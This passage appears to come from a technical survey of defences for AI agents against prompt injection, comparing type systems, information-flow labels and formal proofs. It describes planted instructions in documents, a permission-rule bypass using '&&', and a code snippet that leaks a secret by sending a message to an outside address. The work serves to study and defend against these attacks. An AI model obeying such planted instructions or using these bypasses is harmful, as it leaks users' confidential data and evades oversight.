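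Exceptions, the errors that interrupt a running program, need separate treatment because even a pure function can fail with an error message that contains the contract text. Almost any operation can fail, for instance by dividing by zero or running out of memory, and tracking all these cases in types is considered too cumbersome in Scala. TACIT instead catches the exception at run time and turns it into an ordinary value, which it can seal. In one set of tests, a program that crashed inside `map` therefore looked like a success to the agent, while the user saw nothing. Odersky and colleagues had to instruct the agents to return an explanation instead of throwing an exception.

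Within TACIT's trusted computing base, the library and its wrappers come to about 1,000 lines of Scala, which a person can review. The compiler is far too large for the complete analysis that Anderson's panel wanted, and the features TACIT relies on are new. Capture checking is "still highly experimental and unstable", according to Scala's documentation, and safe mode was only in the compiler's nightly test builds when VirtusLab described it. The underlying type system has machine-checked proofs, but Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that safe mode does not yet have one. Users must also trust the local model not to retain earlier prompts, which no type can guarantee. If it did retain them, it could include one contract's text in an answer about something else.

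### TACIT's leak tests and task performance

To test the wrapper, Odersky and colleagues gave agents a sample software project with a directory of API keys, a database and confidential documents. They paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 planted instructions, for 120 trials. Some tasks, such as summarizing a confidential incident report, needed the secrets. The planted instructions included notes in code comments, fake error messages and ready-made Scala code for reading the secret files. Another 11 trials used the direct and deceptive requests for secrets described earlier. They ran all 131 trials twice for each model, once with the secrets sealed in `Classified` and once with them in plain text, and checked whether any secret appeared in the agent's output.

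| | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | MiniMax M2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Leaks with sealed secrets (131 trials) | 0 | 0 |
| Leaks with plain secrets, planted instructions (120) | 0 | 3 |
| Leaks with plain secrets, requests for secrets (11) | 2 | 8 |
| Ordinary tasks completed, sealed | 99.2% | 90.0% |
| Ordinary tasks completed, plain | 83.3% | 88.3% |

The zeros in the first row are expected from the design, so they mainly confirm that the implementation works. The 120 trials with planted instructions can't show any benefit for Sonnet, since it leaked nothing in them even without the wrapper. The completion rates are more informative, because they show that both models could do useful work on data they couldn't read. Sonnet did worse with plain secrets, and the researchers suggest that it spent too long on some tasks or stopped to warn the user about a planted instruction.

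Odersky and colleagues also tested whether writing typed Scala makes agents perform worse. On τ²-bench, which simulates customer-service conversations, they compared Scala programs with ordinary tool calls for three models, running each task 10 times. Scala did slightly better in every comparison, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software issues, MiniMax M2.5 solved 41.7% with Scala and 43.3% with its usual tools. The models had to retry only 0.3% to 7.9% of snippets after an error, depending on the model and the type of customer service, and one or two attempts were usually enough. Many errors were unrelated to safety. For example, models often caused errors by writing prices with a dollar sign, which can introduce a variable in Scala text.

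The results for the group's next system, LACUNA, are less favourable. When a LACUNA program reaches a call such as `agent[Int]("count the late payments")`, the model writes code for it, and the compiler checks that the code returns a whole number and uses only what is available at that point. The generated code can contain further calls, so the model controls more of the agent's loop than in TACIT. Zhao and colleagues ran LACUNA on 392 τ²-bench tasks with DeepSeek V4 Flash. It solved 76.0%, against 90.0% for ordinary tool calls. They describe this as on par, which is hard to reconcile with a 14-point gap. With the weaker Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, LACUNA solved 29.1% and ordinary tool calls 33.2%, and the compiler rejected 89% of that model's snippets on telecom tasks.

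LACUNA and TACIT have different designs and were tested with different models and tasks, so the later result does not overturn the earlier one. It does show that requiring typed code can hurt an agent's performance. Zhao and colleagues suspect that models have seen less Scala than Python in training. Poor coding slows or stops the agent but does not weaken the protection, because rejected code never runs.

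### Effect types in ELBA

Scala programs can have effects anywhere unless a type forbids them. In Haskell, functions are pure by default, and any effects must appear in a function's type. Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, use this requirement in ELBA, a Haskell library whose `agent` function takes a prompt and a set of permitted functions from the developer. The surrounding program determines the type of result `agent` must produce. ELBA prompts the model for a Haskell program of that type, checks it, and runs it if it passes. Otherwise, the model receives the error message and tries again.

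The simplest case is a public calculator that must return an `Int`, a whole number. A visitor asks it to delete all the files on the server and then compute a factorial. The model might obey, but the function that runs system commands has a type marked `IO`, Haskell's label for input and output, and any program that performs such an action must carry the same label. An `IO Int` is not an `Int`, so ELBA rejects the program, even if the developer did not foresee the attack or write a rule about files.

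Most agents need some effects, and `IO` is too broad because it permits all of them. A developer can instead define a narrower effect type. Zhou and colleagues built an agent that compiles bibliographies and must take every entry from DBLP, a database of computer-science publications. In simplified form, two of its functions have these types:

```
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
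```

The double colon means "has the type", a `DOI` is a publication's standard identifier, and `()` means that the function returns nothing useful. The first function fetches an entry from DBLP and the second adds it to the file. The custom effect type, `BibIO`, covers only the library's own operations. If the agent's program must have the type `BibIO ()`, it can't call Haskell's general function for writing files, because that function has the type `IO ()`.

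This alone would not stop the agent from passing an invented entry to `appendToBibFile`. The wrapper `Trusted` prevents that because its *constructor*, the function that creates values of the type, is private to the library. The agent can only get a `Trusted Bib` by fetching one from DBLP. It can still search, sort and filter freely before choosing what to add.

Zhou and colleagues compare this with two common designs. An agent with a Python interpreter could do the same sorting and filtering, but it could also write an invented entry straight to the file. An agent with a single tool that fetches an entry and adds it in one step can't add an invented entry, but the model has to sort and filter the results itself instead of writing code.

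They then gave agents 100 computer-science topics and asked for a bibliography on each, counting a citation as invented if its authors, year or identifier were wrong. An ordinary agent with a web search tool invented 19 of 1,002 citations, while ELBA invented none of 925. Both used Claude Sonnet 5, but the ordinary agent made about four times as many calls to the model and read about 65 times as much text.

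The result supports the design, but it does not isolate the effect of the types. ELBA took its entries from a curated database, while the other agent wrote them from search results and memory. The single fetch-and-add tool would presumably have reached zero as well. ELBA's advantage over that tool is that it can compute freely, but this test did not compare the two. The types also do not prevent the agent from citing a real but irrelevant paper.

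### Sub-agents and folders

ELBA's model writes a whole program before any search results are available. To choose a next step based on a result, the program calls `agent` again with the result in the new prompt. This call starts a sub-agent, whose program must also match the type that the surrounding code requires. Inside a `BibIO` program, the sub-agent can perform only `BibIO` operations. The parent can restrict it further, for example by requiring plain text, which rules out all effects. The parent can't loosen this restriction by requesting an `IO` program, because the parent's own program would then fail the type check.

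The same method can confine an agent to a folder. Zhou and colleagues define an effect type called `RIO`, whose only operations are to read files, write them and list directories. These operations take a `Path` instead of a file name. A `Path` is a capability for a folder or file, and its constructor is hidden. The contracts agent could write:

```
summarize :: Path -> RIO ()
summarize folder = do
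    text <- readRIO (folder // "acme.txt")
    writeRIO (folder // "summary.txt")
             (agent defs ("Summarize: " ++ text))
```

The `//` operator narrows a `Path` to a file or folder inside it. The compiler can't determine where a path will lead, so the operator checks at run time. It follows any links on the disk and fails if the result lies outside the original folder. The sub-agent in the last line reads the contract, including the planted sentence, but must return plain text. If it follows the planted sentence and writes code to send the contract to the outside address, that code fails the type check.

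Zhou and colleagues present `RIO` as a design and do not measure it. They argue for it by citing weaknesses in permission rules that match the text of shell commands. In March 2026, a user reported that Claude Code checked only the first part of a command joined with `&&`, so a forbidden command could follow a permitted one. A short Python program on the command line can also open a file that the rules forbid. An operating-system sandbox would catch both cases, but it normally sets one fixed list of folders for the whole process, whereas a program can pass each sub-agent a narrower `Path`.

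### The soundness theorem

Zhou and colleagues prove that adding agents to a typed language does not weaken its guarantees. They call the sequence of tool calls with observable effects that a program makes a *trace*, and write traces(*e*) for the set of traces that a program *e* can produce. A type *t* guarantees a property *P* if the following holds for every program *e* in the host language, such as Haskell:

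if *e* has type *t*, then *P*(traces(*e*)) is true

For `BibIO`, the property is that the program writes only data from DBLP. The theorem states that every such guarantee of the host language still holds when agent calls are added to the language.

The proof turns any program with agent calls into an ordinary program that behaves identically. Each agent call has a required type *t* and a limit *n* on how deeply further calls may nest. For every *t* and *n*, Zhou and colleagues define an ordinary function *a*(*t*, *n*) to take the call's place:

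- *a*(*t*, 0) returns no result.
- *a*(*t*, *n* + 1) asks the model for a program. If the program has type *t*, the function replaces every agent call inside it with the matching ordinary function and runs it. Otherwise it returns no result.

Calls inside the generated program have a limit of *n* or less, so the replacements they need already exist. Replacing all the agent calls in *e* gives an ordinary program *e*′ of the same type. By induction on *n*, *e*′ produces the same traces as *e*. The host language guarantees *P* for *e*′, so *P* also holds for *e*.

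The theorem's main attraction is that it makes no assumption about the model's intentions, since even a hostile model's programs have to pass the check. But the theorem only carries over guarantees that the host language already provides. If the compiler accepts a program it should reject, or if the bibliography library accidentally exposes its constructor, the agent's program can exploit the flaw just as any other program could.

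The proof also assumes that the language can check and run new code while a program is running, and that nesting has a limit. The scaffold must be part of the typed program, since a scaffold in unchecked code could do things that the types forbid. The proof treats the model as a function that always gives the same answer to the same request. Real models can give different answers, but Zhou and colleagues consider this irrelevant to the properties they study, and suggest storing the answers where the variation matters.

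A trace includes tool calls but not requests to the model. The sub-agent in `summarize` has an effect-free type, yet ELBA sends it the whole contract, and if the model runs in the cloud, the provider receives the text. The theorem still holds, but it does not cover this leak. TACIT prevents the leak by keeping the text sealed and sending it only to the local model.

### Code that escapes the check

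Haskell and Scala both have features that let code bypass the language's own rules. Haskell's `unsafePerformIO`, for example, gives a computation with effects the type of a pure one. ELBA can exclude it by using Safe Haskell, an established subset of the language designed for running untrusted code. Scala's safe mode serves the same purpose but is much newer and less proven. Zhao and colleagues advise that without safe mode, developers should treat agent code like any other untrusted program, even if it passes all the type checks.

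External commands are a harder problem. They run outside the typed language, so the compiler can't limit what they do. Odersky and colleagues accept that the guarantee is then only as strong as the list of permitted commands. They recommend keeping the list short and, for important systems, running the whole process in a sandbox. Their examples of safe commands include a questionable one, Scala's build tool `sbt`. An `sbt` build file is itself Scala code that runs outside safe mode, so an agent that can edit the file and start `sbt` can run any code. Programming agents face this problem constantly, because running a project's tests means running code that the agent may have just written.

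Even a pure function can leak information through timing, for example by taking longer when a contract contains a certain word. Odersky and colleagues leave such leaks out of scope.

### The cost of typed interfaces

Most agent frameworks use Python, whose types offer no comparable protection. A company that adopts TACIT needs a typed Scala function for each tool. Odersky and colleagues argue that the difficult part, the shared library, already exists. The interfaces for τ²-bench's airline and retail tools took a few hundred lines each, about as much as the tool descriptions they replaced. Agents can draft such interfaces for people to review. The reviewers must understand the types, however, because an interface that returns contract text as an ordinary `String` removes the protection without causing an error.

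Type systems also reject some harmless programs. One agent in the TACIT tests wrote a function to print the first lines of a file, but declared its parameter as a file object without capabilities. The compiler rejected the function, although running it would have been harmless. Such errors do little harm when the agent can correct them. Zhou and colleagues ran ELBA 2,688 times on AgentDojo, a benchmark that measures whether agents finish tasks and whether planted instructions succeed. ELBA needed an average of 0.13 retries per run, and only seven runs exhausted their retries.

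A strict policy is a bigger obstacle, since rewriting the code can't help if the policy forbids what the task requires. VirtusLab warns that an agent becomes much less useful if the company using it classifies too much of its data. On AgentDojo, both TACIT and ELBA with its data-labelling policies stopped almost all attacks, but ELBA finished far fewer tasks with those policies than without them. Zhou and colleagues reply that a strict filter can still reduce the number of approvals people have to give, because actions that pass can go ahead without approval and a person needs to review only the rest.

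The sealed wrapper also has a drawback, because the cloud model must write its code without seeing the text. If one contract lists its penalties in a table and another in a footnote, a single fixed function may miss one of them. LACUNA addresses this by letting the function passed to `map` call the trusted local model, which can read the text and write code to suit it. The compiler checks that code under the same rule, so it must also be pure.

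### Wrong answers that pass every check

A program with the right type can still do the wrong thing. It might compare the wrong two contracts or report a £10,000 penalty as £1,000. Odersky and colleagues treat correctness as a separate problem, which is reasonable for honest mistakes but less convincing for deliberate attacks. They argue that a planted instruction can cause real harm only by sending private data somewhere forbidden or using a capability the agent was never given. The instruction to leave out the penalty clause does neither. If the local model follows it, the sealed summary lacks the clause and every type is still correct.

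LACUNA's developers, who include Odersky, are more cautious. They concede that their system does not stop an attacker who gets the model to misuse a capability it needs for the task, and that the developer using it must keep each grant as small as possible. They hope to add types that carry conditions, such as a number within a given range or a list of a fixed length. These would catch a penalty of minus £10,000. To catch the missing clause, somebody would first have to express "a complete summary" as a condition that a compiler can check.

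## Tracking where data comes from and where it may go

TACIT's wrapper puts data in one of two states, sealed or unsealed, which is too coarse for many companies. The lawyer's manager may be allowed to read a contract that the finance department may not, and a request from the lawyer deserves more trust than a sentence the other party typed into the document. *Information-flow control* handles these differences by attaching a label to each piece of data, tracking the data and anything derived from it through the computation, and checking the label wherever data leaves. A sandbox misses the leak in the contracts example because it limits which files and addresses a program can reach but does not track the text that moves between them.

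### Labels and how they combine

A label usually has two parts. The secrecy part can be the set of people who may read the data. The trust part, called integrity, is T (trusted) if only trusted sources influenced the data and U (untrusted) otherwise. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a Microsoft agent system that uses such labels.

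When a program computes *z* from *x* and *y*, the result takes the combined label of its inputs. The symbol ⊔, pronounced "join", stands for the combination:

label(*z*) = label(*x*) ⊔ label(*y*)

For trust, T ⊔ T = T, and anything joined with U is U. For secrecy, only people who may read both inputs may read the result, so the join keeps the readers that the two sets share. For labels with both parts, the formula is:

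(*t*₁, *R*₁) ⊔ (*t*₂, *R*₂) = (*t*₁ ⊔ *t*₂, *R*₁ ∩ *R*₂)

A join can leave a label unchanged or make it more restrictive, but never less restrictive. FIDES also uses a join to label a language model's answer, combining the labels of everything in the model's *context*, the text the model reads before it responds. It does not try to work out which parts of that text shaped the answer.

Before each tool call, ordinary code checks the labels. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, define two checks:

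- **Trusted action:** the decision to make the call, and every argument that matters for safety, must carry the label T.
- **Permitted flow:** everyone who will receive the data must be among its permitted readers, so recipients ⊆ *R*.

They require the first check for tools with serious consequences. A call to a tool that sends data somewhere may go ahead if it passes either check.

### The contracts agent, label by label

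Suppose the folder holds contracts with two other companies, Acme and Birch. The lawyer and her manager may read both, and the finance department may read only Acme's. Both contracts are untrusted because outsiders wrote parts of them. The lawyer's request is trusted and contains no secrets. The labels develop as follows:

| Step | Label of the new text | Label of the context afterwards |
|---|---|---|
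| The lawyer makes her request | (T, everyone) | (T, everyone) |
| The agent reads Acme's contract | (U, {lawyer, manager, finance}) | (U, {lawyer, manager, finance}) |
| The agent reads Birch's contract | (U, {lawyer, manager}) | (U, {lawyer, manager}) |
| The model writes the summary | (U, {lawyer, manager}) | (U, {lawyer, manager}) |

If the model follows the planted sentence and calls the sending function, the scaffold refuses the call because it fails both checks. The decision to make the call came from a context labeled U, and the outside address does not belong to the lawyer or her manager. Paraphrasing or translating the contract first would not change this, because the new text inherits the label.

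The agent may still write the summary to a file that only the lawyer and her manager can open. The decision to write is untrusted, but the check permits the flow because both readers are in the set. If the finance department could also open the file, the check would refuse the call, because the summary draws on Birch's contract.

The cloud model reads both contracts in this calculation, so its provider receives them. Costa and colleagues trust the model and treat requests to it as harmless, but they note that a developer who disagrees can apply the checks to those requests too. With the reader sets above, the checks would stop the agent as soon as it tried to show the model a contract.

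### Noninterference and the branch that never runs

The strongest standard in this field is *noninterference*, which requires that secret inputs not affect what an unauthorized observer sees. If two runs of the contracts agent differ only in the text of the contracts, an outsider must see the same thing in both. The same standard applies to trust, where it requires that untrusted inputs not affect any result labeled T.

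Following copies of the text is not enough to achieve this. A program could check a contract and send "hello" to an outside address only if the contract contains a large penalty. The message includes nothing from the contract, but its arrival reveals that the penalty exists. The usual remedy is to treat everything inside a branch as secret if the decision to enter the branch depended on a secret.

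This still leaves a gap, which Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found in CaMeL, a well-known agent system from 2025. Adapted to the contracts, their example looks like this:

```
tmp   = true
found = true
if penalty > 10000: tmp = false
if tmp: found = false
if found: send(outside_address, "hello")
```

If the penalty is large, the third line sets `tmp` to false and marks it secret. The fourth line's branch then doesn't run, so `found` stays true and keeps its public label. The last line sends the message, which passes the check because nothing in it is labeled secret. If the penalty is small, `found` becomes false and no message goes out. CaMeL raises a variable's label only in a branch that runs, so it misses this leak of the penalty's size. The computer scientist J. S. Fenton described the trick decades ago.

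A stricter rule forbids a program to change anything public inside a branch that depends on a secret. It would stop this program at `tmp = false`. An observer might notice the stop and learn one fact about the penalty. Most guarantees in the field allow a leak of this size. In CaMeL, however, an ordinary Python loop outside the part of the system that tracks labels restarts blocked programs. Garby and colleagues point out that an attacker could use this loop to repeat the leak and extract a whole secret one bit at a time.

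FIDES has a more modest goal, called *explicit secrecy*. It covers secret data that the agent passes directly into a tool call, but not what an observer could infer from which tools the agent calls. Costa and colleagues rejected full noninterference as too restrictive because, in their view, it would effectively forbid any tool call with publicly visible results once the agent had called a tool that might read secrets.

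### What the LLMbda calculus proves

LLMbda is a very small programming language, or *calculus*, built for proving theorems about agents. A program in it can send a prompt to a model, run code from the reply, copy a conversation for a side task, or clear it. Every value has a label, and so does the conversation.

Models give varying answers, so noninterference has to compare probabilities. Take two inputs *a* and *b* that look identical to some observer. Let μ*ₐ* and μ*ᵦ* give the probability of each outcome the observer can see. These probabilities may add up to less than 1, because some runs never finish or a check stops them. The main theorem states that there is always a third distribution ω, with a total of at most 1, such that for every outcome:

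μ*ₐ* ≤ ω and μ*ᵦ* ≤ ω

If every run finishes, both totals are 1, so μ*ₐ* and μ*ᵦ* must be equal and the observer learns nothing. Otherwise, the statistical distance between the two distributions is at most the average of the two probabilities of not finishing. If 10% of runs fail to finish in each case, the probability of any visible outcome can differ by at most 10 percentage points.

For ω, the proof uses the distribution from a second way of running the program, which skips a computation as soon as its label rises above what the observer may see. This version never uses hidden data, so it gives the same distribution for *a* and *b*. It also produces each visible outcome at least as often as the original does.

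The theorem covers every program in the calculus, including programs that run code written by a model, and it holds whatever the model replies. Garby and colleagues checked the proof with Lean, a language for writing proofs that a computer can verify. They also used Lean to write the program that runs the agents and proved that it follows the calculus, so the guarantee applies to working software as well as to the mathematics. But the guarantee depends on correct labels. A confidential contract marked as public gets no more protection than any other public text.

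### One model to plan and another to read

In the calculation above, reading one contract made the model's whole context untrusted. The *dual-model pattern*, which Simon Willison proposed in 2023, avoids this with two models. A privileged model plans the task and calls tools but never sees untrusted text. A quarantined model reads the text but has no tools. The planner refers to the text by a variable name, much as TACIT's agent handles a sealed value:

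```
contract = read("acme.txt")
summary  = ask_quarantined("Summarize this", contract)
write("summary.txt", summary)
```

The planted sentence reaches only the quarantined model, which can't send anything. It can still produce an empty summary or omit the penalty clause.

CaMeL, by Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues, builds on this pattern. The planner writes a program in a restricted form of Python before it sees any data, and a special interpreter runs the program while tracking labels. Planning in advance prevents injected text from determining the next step, but it also prevents the agent from adapting its plan to legitimate data. For example, the agent can't open a to-do list and then work out how to handle each item. Odersky and colleagues add that CaMeL's version of Python lacks user-defined and recursive functions.

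FIDES is more flexible. It hides a result in a variable only if showing it would make the context's label more restrictive, so the planner can read trusted data directly. The planner can also query the quarantined model and restrict its output to a limited set of answers. Suppose the user wants a calendar entry if any of three emails requests a meeting. The planner queries the quarantined model for whether there is such a request and reads only the yes or no. If the answer is yes, the quarantined model extracts the details into another variable, which the planner passes to the calendar without reading it. The planner may also read a variable in full, but its context then takes on the variable's label, and the checks block some later calls.

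ELBA uses LIO, an established Haskell library for information-flow control, instead of a special planner. An LIO computation has a *current label*, which rises whenever the computation reads something more restricted. LIO checks this label before each write. If a program fetches a page from an untrusted website and then tries to write the content to the user's data, LIO stops it with an error. This check happens while the program runs, so here ELBA loses the advantage of rejecting bad code in advance.

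The function `toLabeled` runs part of a program separately and returns the result in a sealed form, without raising the current label outside that part. If that part is a sub-agent, this works like the dual-model pattern, except that the sub-agent can keep its tools. In an example from Zhou and colleagues, a sub-agent reads untrusted data and drafts a direct message. The parent agent can pass the sealed draft, without reading it, to the sending function, which checks the draft's label.

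Odersky and colleagues argue that run-time tracking such as CaMeL's loses its markers once text enters a model's conversation. FIDES and LLMbda avoid this problem by labelling the conversation itself, but one restricted document then affects everything the model does afterwards.

The designs also differ in how far they trust the planner. Kolluri and colleagues assume that the planning model is trustworthy, as they say FIDES and CaMeL do. Under their either-or rule, a planner acting in a trusted context may send data to someone outside the reader set, because the system assumes the user wants this. This helps if the lawyer asks the agent to send a contract to an outside expert. But a planner with its own aims could send the contract to anyone, even before reading any untrusted text. Requiring both checks would prevent that, but the lawyer would then need to approve the message to the expert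 separately.

### Results on AgentDojo

AgentDojo contains simulated tasks in four domains: banking, office work (called "workspace"), the messaging service Slack, and travel. Each attack combines a user's task with a planted instruction.

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES with GPT-4o and one of the benchmark's strongest attacks. After they removed cases that the benchmark misjudged, 152 injections succeeded against a basic agent loop without policies and 21 against FIDES without policies. With policies on, none succeeded against either. This result is partly due to how they assigned labels. They marked a data field as untrusted if any of the benchmark's attacks used it, but a company labelling its own data wouldn't have a list of attacks to work from.

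The policies prevented many tasks from being completed. On Slack, without attacks, they lowered the basic loop's completion rate from 93.3% to 20.0%, while FIDES completed 47.6% of tasks with policies on. Averaged over the four domains, FIDES's completion rate was about 8 percentage points higher than the basic loop's under the same policies, and 16 points higher with OpenAI's o1, a stronger model. With GPT-4o, the basic loop did better than FIDES on travel, because many travel tools are allowed to run in an untrusted context and FIDES often handled its variables badly.

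Odersky and colleagues ran TACIT in all four domains and compared their results with the figures CaMeL's developers had published for the same models.

| Tasks completed | CaMeL, Gemini 2.5 Pro | TACIT, Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL, o4-mini | TACIT, o4-mini |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 52.8% | 56.9% | 62.5% | 59.0% |
| Workspace | 53.8% | 50.5% | 81.4% | 52.9% |
| Slack | 48.6% | 40.0% | 68.6% | 47.6% |
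| Travel | 1.4% | 64.3% | 74.3% | 68.6% |

They call the two systems comparable, which is true for banking but not for the whole table. CaMeL leads in six of the eight comparisons, including by more than 28 points on workspace tasks with o4-mini. TACIT's one large win is on travel tasks with Gemini, where CaMeL failed almost completely. CaMeL scored 74.3% on travel tasks with o4-mini, so the failure probably comes from how Gemini worked with CaMeL and not from CaMeL's design alone.

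Each system had one successful attack with o4-mini and none with Gemini. The one against TACIT counted as successful only because of how the benchmark scores attacks. A planted hotel review recommended a rival hotel, and the agent booked the right hotel but quoted the review to the user. The benchmark counted this as a success for the attacker because the quote named the rival, although the policy allowed the agent to show public reviews.

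Garby and colleagues tested an LLMbda agent called RANDORI on the banking tasks. RANDORI first writes and debugs its program in an artificial copy of the bank, because error messages from real, untrusted data would make the program untrusted. With GPT-5.2 and no attacks, it completed 36 of 48 runs. CaMeL completed 18 with its policies on and 32 with them off. But RANDORI enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, and there were only 16 distinct tasks, so the size of its lead is uncertain. Attacks succeeded in two of the 1,296 attacked runs across three models. The theorem does not rule out such failures, because RANDORI's own code may relabel untrusted data as trusted.

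On Slack, Zhou and colleagues compared ELBA with CaMeL using newer models. Without attacks, the systems completed the following numbers of the 21 tasks:

| Model | ELBA, policies on | CaMeL, policies on | ELBA, policies off | CaMeL, policies off |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 10 | 5 | 18 | 15 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 9 | 6 | 16 | 16 |
| GPT-5.4 | 10 | 5 | 16 | 17 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 8 | 4 | 14 | 13 |

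With policies on, ELBA completed roughly twice as many tasks as CaMeL, and it kept a similar lead under attack. Unlike CaMeL, ELBA can read a message and then decide what to do, but it took about three times as long to run. The two systems also enforced different policies. ELBA lowers an agent's privileges to those of whatever source the agent has just read, and part of its lead may come from that policy.

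In the same comparison, every model resisted the injection in all 105 of the benchmark's task-and-injection pairs, in each of three attack formats, even with policies off. The standard attacks therefore couldn't show whether the policies added any security. A perfect score on them is weak evidence that a defence works, at least on Slack with models this good. It is also weak evidence that the models are safe, because a real attacker can keep adjusting the injected text until it works. Zhou and colleagues mention GPT-Red, OpenAI's automated attack system, which consistently got past GPT-5.5's defences.

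They therefore simulated an injection that always works. Whenever a sub-agent's input contained the marker of a planted instruction, they deleted the sub-agent's real task and gave it only the attacker's text. They ran the 105 pairs seven times for each model, or 735 attacks per model. ELBA stopped 425 to 621 of these with policies off, depending on the model, and all 735 for every model with policies on. The number of completed tasks fell from 494–558 with policies off to 294–351 with them on.

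This test is much more informative than the standard one because it assumes the model has already failed and measures what the surrounding software does next. The zero required some judgement. The benchmark counted 29 of the 2,940 runs with policies on as successful attacks because the agent had opened a fixed web address, but Zhou and colleagues reviewed each one and found that no data had leaked.

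Costa and colleagues found that many banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which is also what a prompt injection makes an agent do. Labels record only that the instruction came from an untrusted file, so a check based on them has to refuse both, and the legitimate tasks are lost.

### Label creep

Because joins never relax a label, restrictions accumulate, which is called *label creep*. Suppose the contracts agent keeps its conversation after writing the summary, and the lawyer asks it to invite a client to lunch. The invitation contains nothing secret, but the context's label is still (U, {lawyer, manager}). The client isn't in that set, so the system refuses to send the invitation.

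Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026), in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, simulated how it spreads among several agents. They generated random tasks of 4 to 20 tool calls, many of which depended on one another, and divided the calls among the agents. Most of the experiments used the tasks with 20 calls. Some calls introduced a secret label. An agent that received secret data, even just to pass it on, kept the label for good, and nobody could remove it. The measure of harm was:

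loss = calls that introduce the secret label or run under it / all calls

The loss depended on how the agents were connected. With five working agents and four sensitive calls, sending everything through a central coordinator added about 5 percentage points of loss compared with an ideal network for each task. A ring added about 3 points, and direct links between all agents added none. Direct links help because data doesn't pass through other agents, which would pick up its label just by forwarding it.

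Using more agents also reduced the loss, since each one keeps its context separate. But if every pair of agents is linked, 5 agents need 10 links and 20 agents need 190, and someone has to monitor them all. Giving the sensitive tools to a few dedicated agents helped too. For example, a company could let one agent read contracts and another handle invitations.

Even the ideal networks lost much of their usefulness when many calls were sensitive, so Gregory and colleagues conclude that systems also need a way to relax labels. The simulation ran no language model, and it counted every call under a secret label as a loss, even if a real policy would have allowed it. The ranking of the designs is therefore more credible than the exact percentages.

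### Approved release and planning around labels

One remedy is to make the labels more accurate. Costa and colleagues describe a method that looks for the parts of the context that influenced an answer and generates the answer again from those parts alone. The lunch invitation could then go without the contracts' label, but the method requires extra calls to the model.

The other approach is to relax a label deliberately. *Declassification* widens the set of permitted readers, and *endorsement* relabels untrusted data as trusted. Both make exceptions to noninterference, so the hard part is limiting what else those exceptions let through.

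FIDES can allow exceptions for answers with few possible values. A yes or no carries at most one bit of information, and a choice among *n* categories carries at most log₂ *n* bits, which is too little to hold a planted instruction. One bit can still do harm if it determines whether the agent pays an invoice. Garby and colleagues worry that on a given run, nobody can tell a harmless exception from a leak that looks the same. LLMbda instead requires the program to contain an explicit `endorse` command, which a reviewer can find. Garby and colleagues' second theorem shows that endorsing data can't expose secrets, whatever untrusted text an attacker supplies.

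Kolluri and colleagues try to reduce the number of exceptions an agent needs. In earlier systems, the planner wasn't given the policies and triggered them by accident. Their agent, PRUDENTIA, extends FIDES by giving the planner its context's label and each tool's rule. Before it opens a variable, the planner must explain why it needs the content and list the calls it expects to make afterwards. For example, it might send the lunch invitation before opening the contract.

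PRUDENTIA can also ask the user to endorse data. If an email contains a to-do list with ten items that each need a protected tool, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten tool calls. PRUDENTIA does not let the user declassify private data in the same way, because whether someone should receive it depends too much on the particular message. The user must approve each call that would share private data.

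To measure the benefit, Kolluri and colleagues count how often an agent needs a person. For a set of *n* tasks:

TCR@*k* = (tasks completed with at most *k* human approvals) / *n*

They argue that earlier studies made information-flow control look worse than it is by comparing protected agents that got no approvals (*k* = 0) with unprotected agents that could do anything. Many agents already ask for approval before consequential actions, and labels show which of those requests are unnecessary. On AgentDojo, PRUDENTIA completed up to 9% more tasks than FIDES without any approvals and reduced the total number of approvals by a factor of up to 1.9. It needed no approvals on WASP, another benchmark, whose tasks never require the agent to choose its next step from untrusted data.

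These figures include only tasks the agent completed, and they assume the person would have approved every request. They don't measure how well people judge what they endorse, and Claude Code's users already approve nearly every prompt they see. Endorsing a whole document is also a bigger decision than approving one call. If the lawyer endorses Acme's contract without noticing the white text on the white page, the planted sentence and the address it contains become trusted. Under the either-or rule, the agent may then send the contract out.

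## Proving an agent's plan or framework safe before it acts

Types can guarantee that an agent's program touches only the files in one folder, but ordinary types can't guarantee that it deletes two old drafts and leaves the signed contracts alone. *Formal verification* can, by proving mathematically that a program meets a *specification*, an exact statement of what the program must and must not do. Type checking is a lighter form of formal verification in which the compiler proves simple facts automatically. Stronger facts require longer proofs, which somebody has to find.

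### Proof-carrying code

In *Proof-Carrying Code* (Necula, 1997), the computer that will run a program, called the host, first sets a safety policy. The program's supplier must then formally prove that the program obeys the policy and send the proof along with the program. The host runs the program only if the proof is valid. Necula notes that the host can check the proof quickly, without using cryptography or consulting anyone else.

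The method relies on proofs being much easier to check than to find. Each step of a formal proof must follow from earlier steps by a fixed rule, so a checker only has to confirm each step in turn. *Provably safe systems* (Tegmark and Omohundro, 2023) cites a checker for MetaMath, a language for formal mathematics, that takes only 300 lines of Python. A person can read all of it, as Anderson's third requirement demands. Finding a proof can be very hard because the number of candidate proofs grows exponentially with their length.

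The supplier's motives therefore don't matter, because even a hostile model can't produce a valid proof for a program that violates the policy. A digital signature, by contrast, shows who sent a program but not what it does.

A developer could try to prove safety properties of the plan an agent writes for one task, of the scaffold, or of the model itself. Plans are short, but every new plan needs a new proof. A proof about the scaffold holds until somebody changes the code, but it covers only what passes through the scaffold. A proof about the model could in principle cover everything it outputs. Such a proof is far out of reach for large language models, and even Tegmark and Omohundro, who advocate proofs almost everywhere, consider the models' inner workings too messy to verify easily.

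### Checking a whole plan before it runs

*Guardians of the Agents* (Meijer, 2025) proposes that the model write a complete workflow instead of calling tools one at a time. The workflow lists each tool call, a name for its result and the next step. Other software verifies the workflow and runs it only if it passes.

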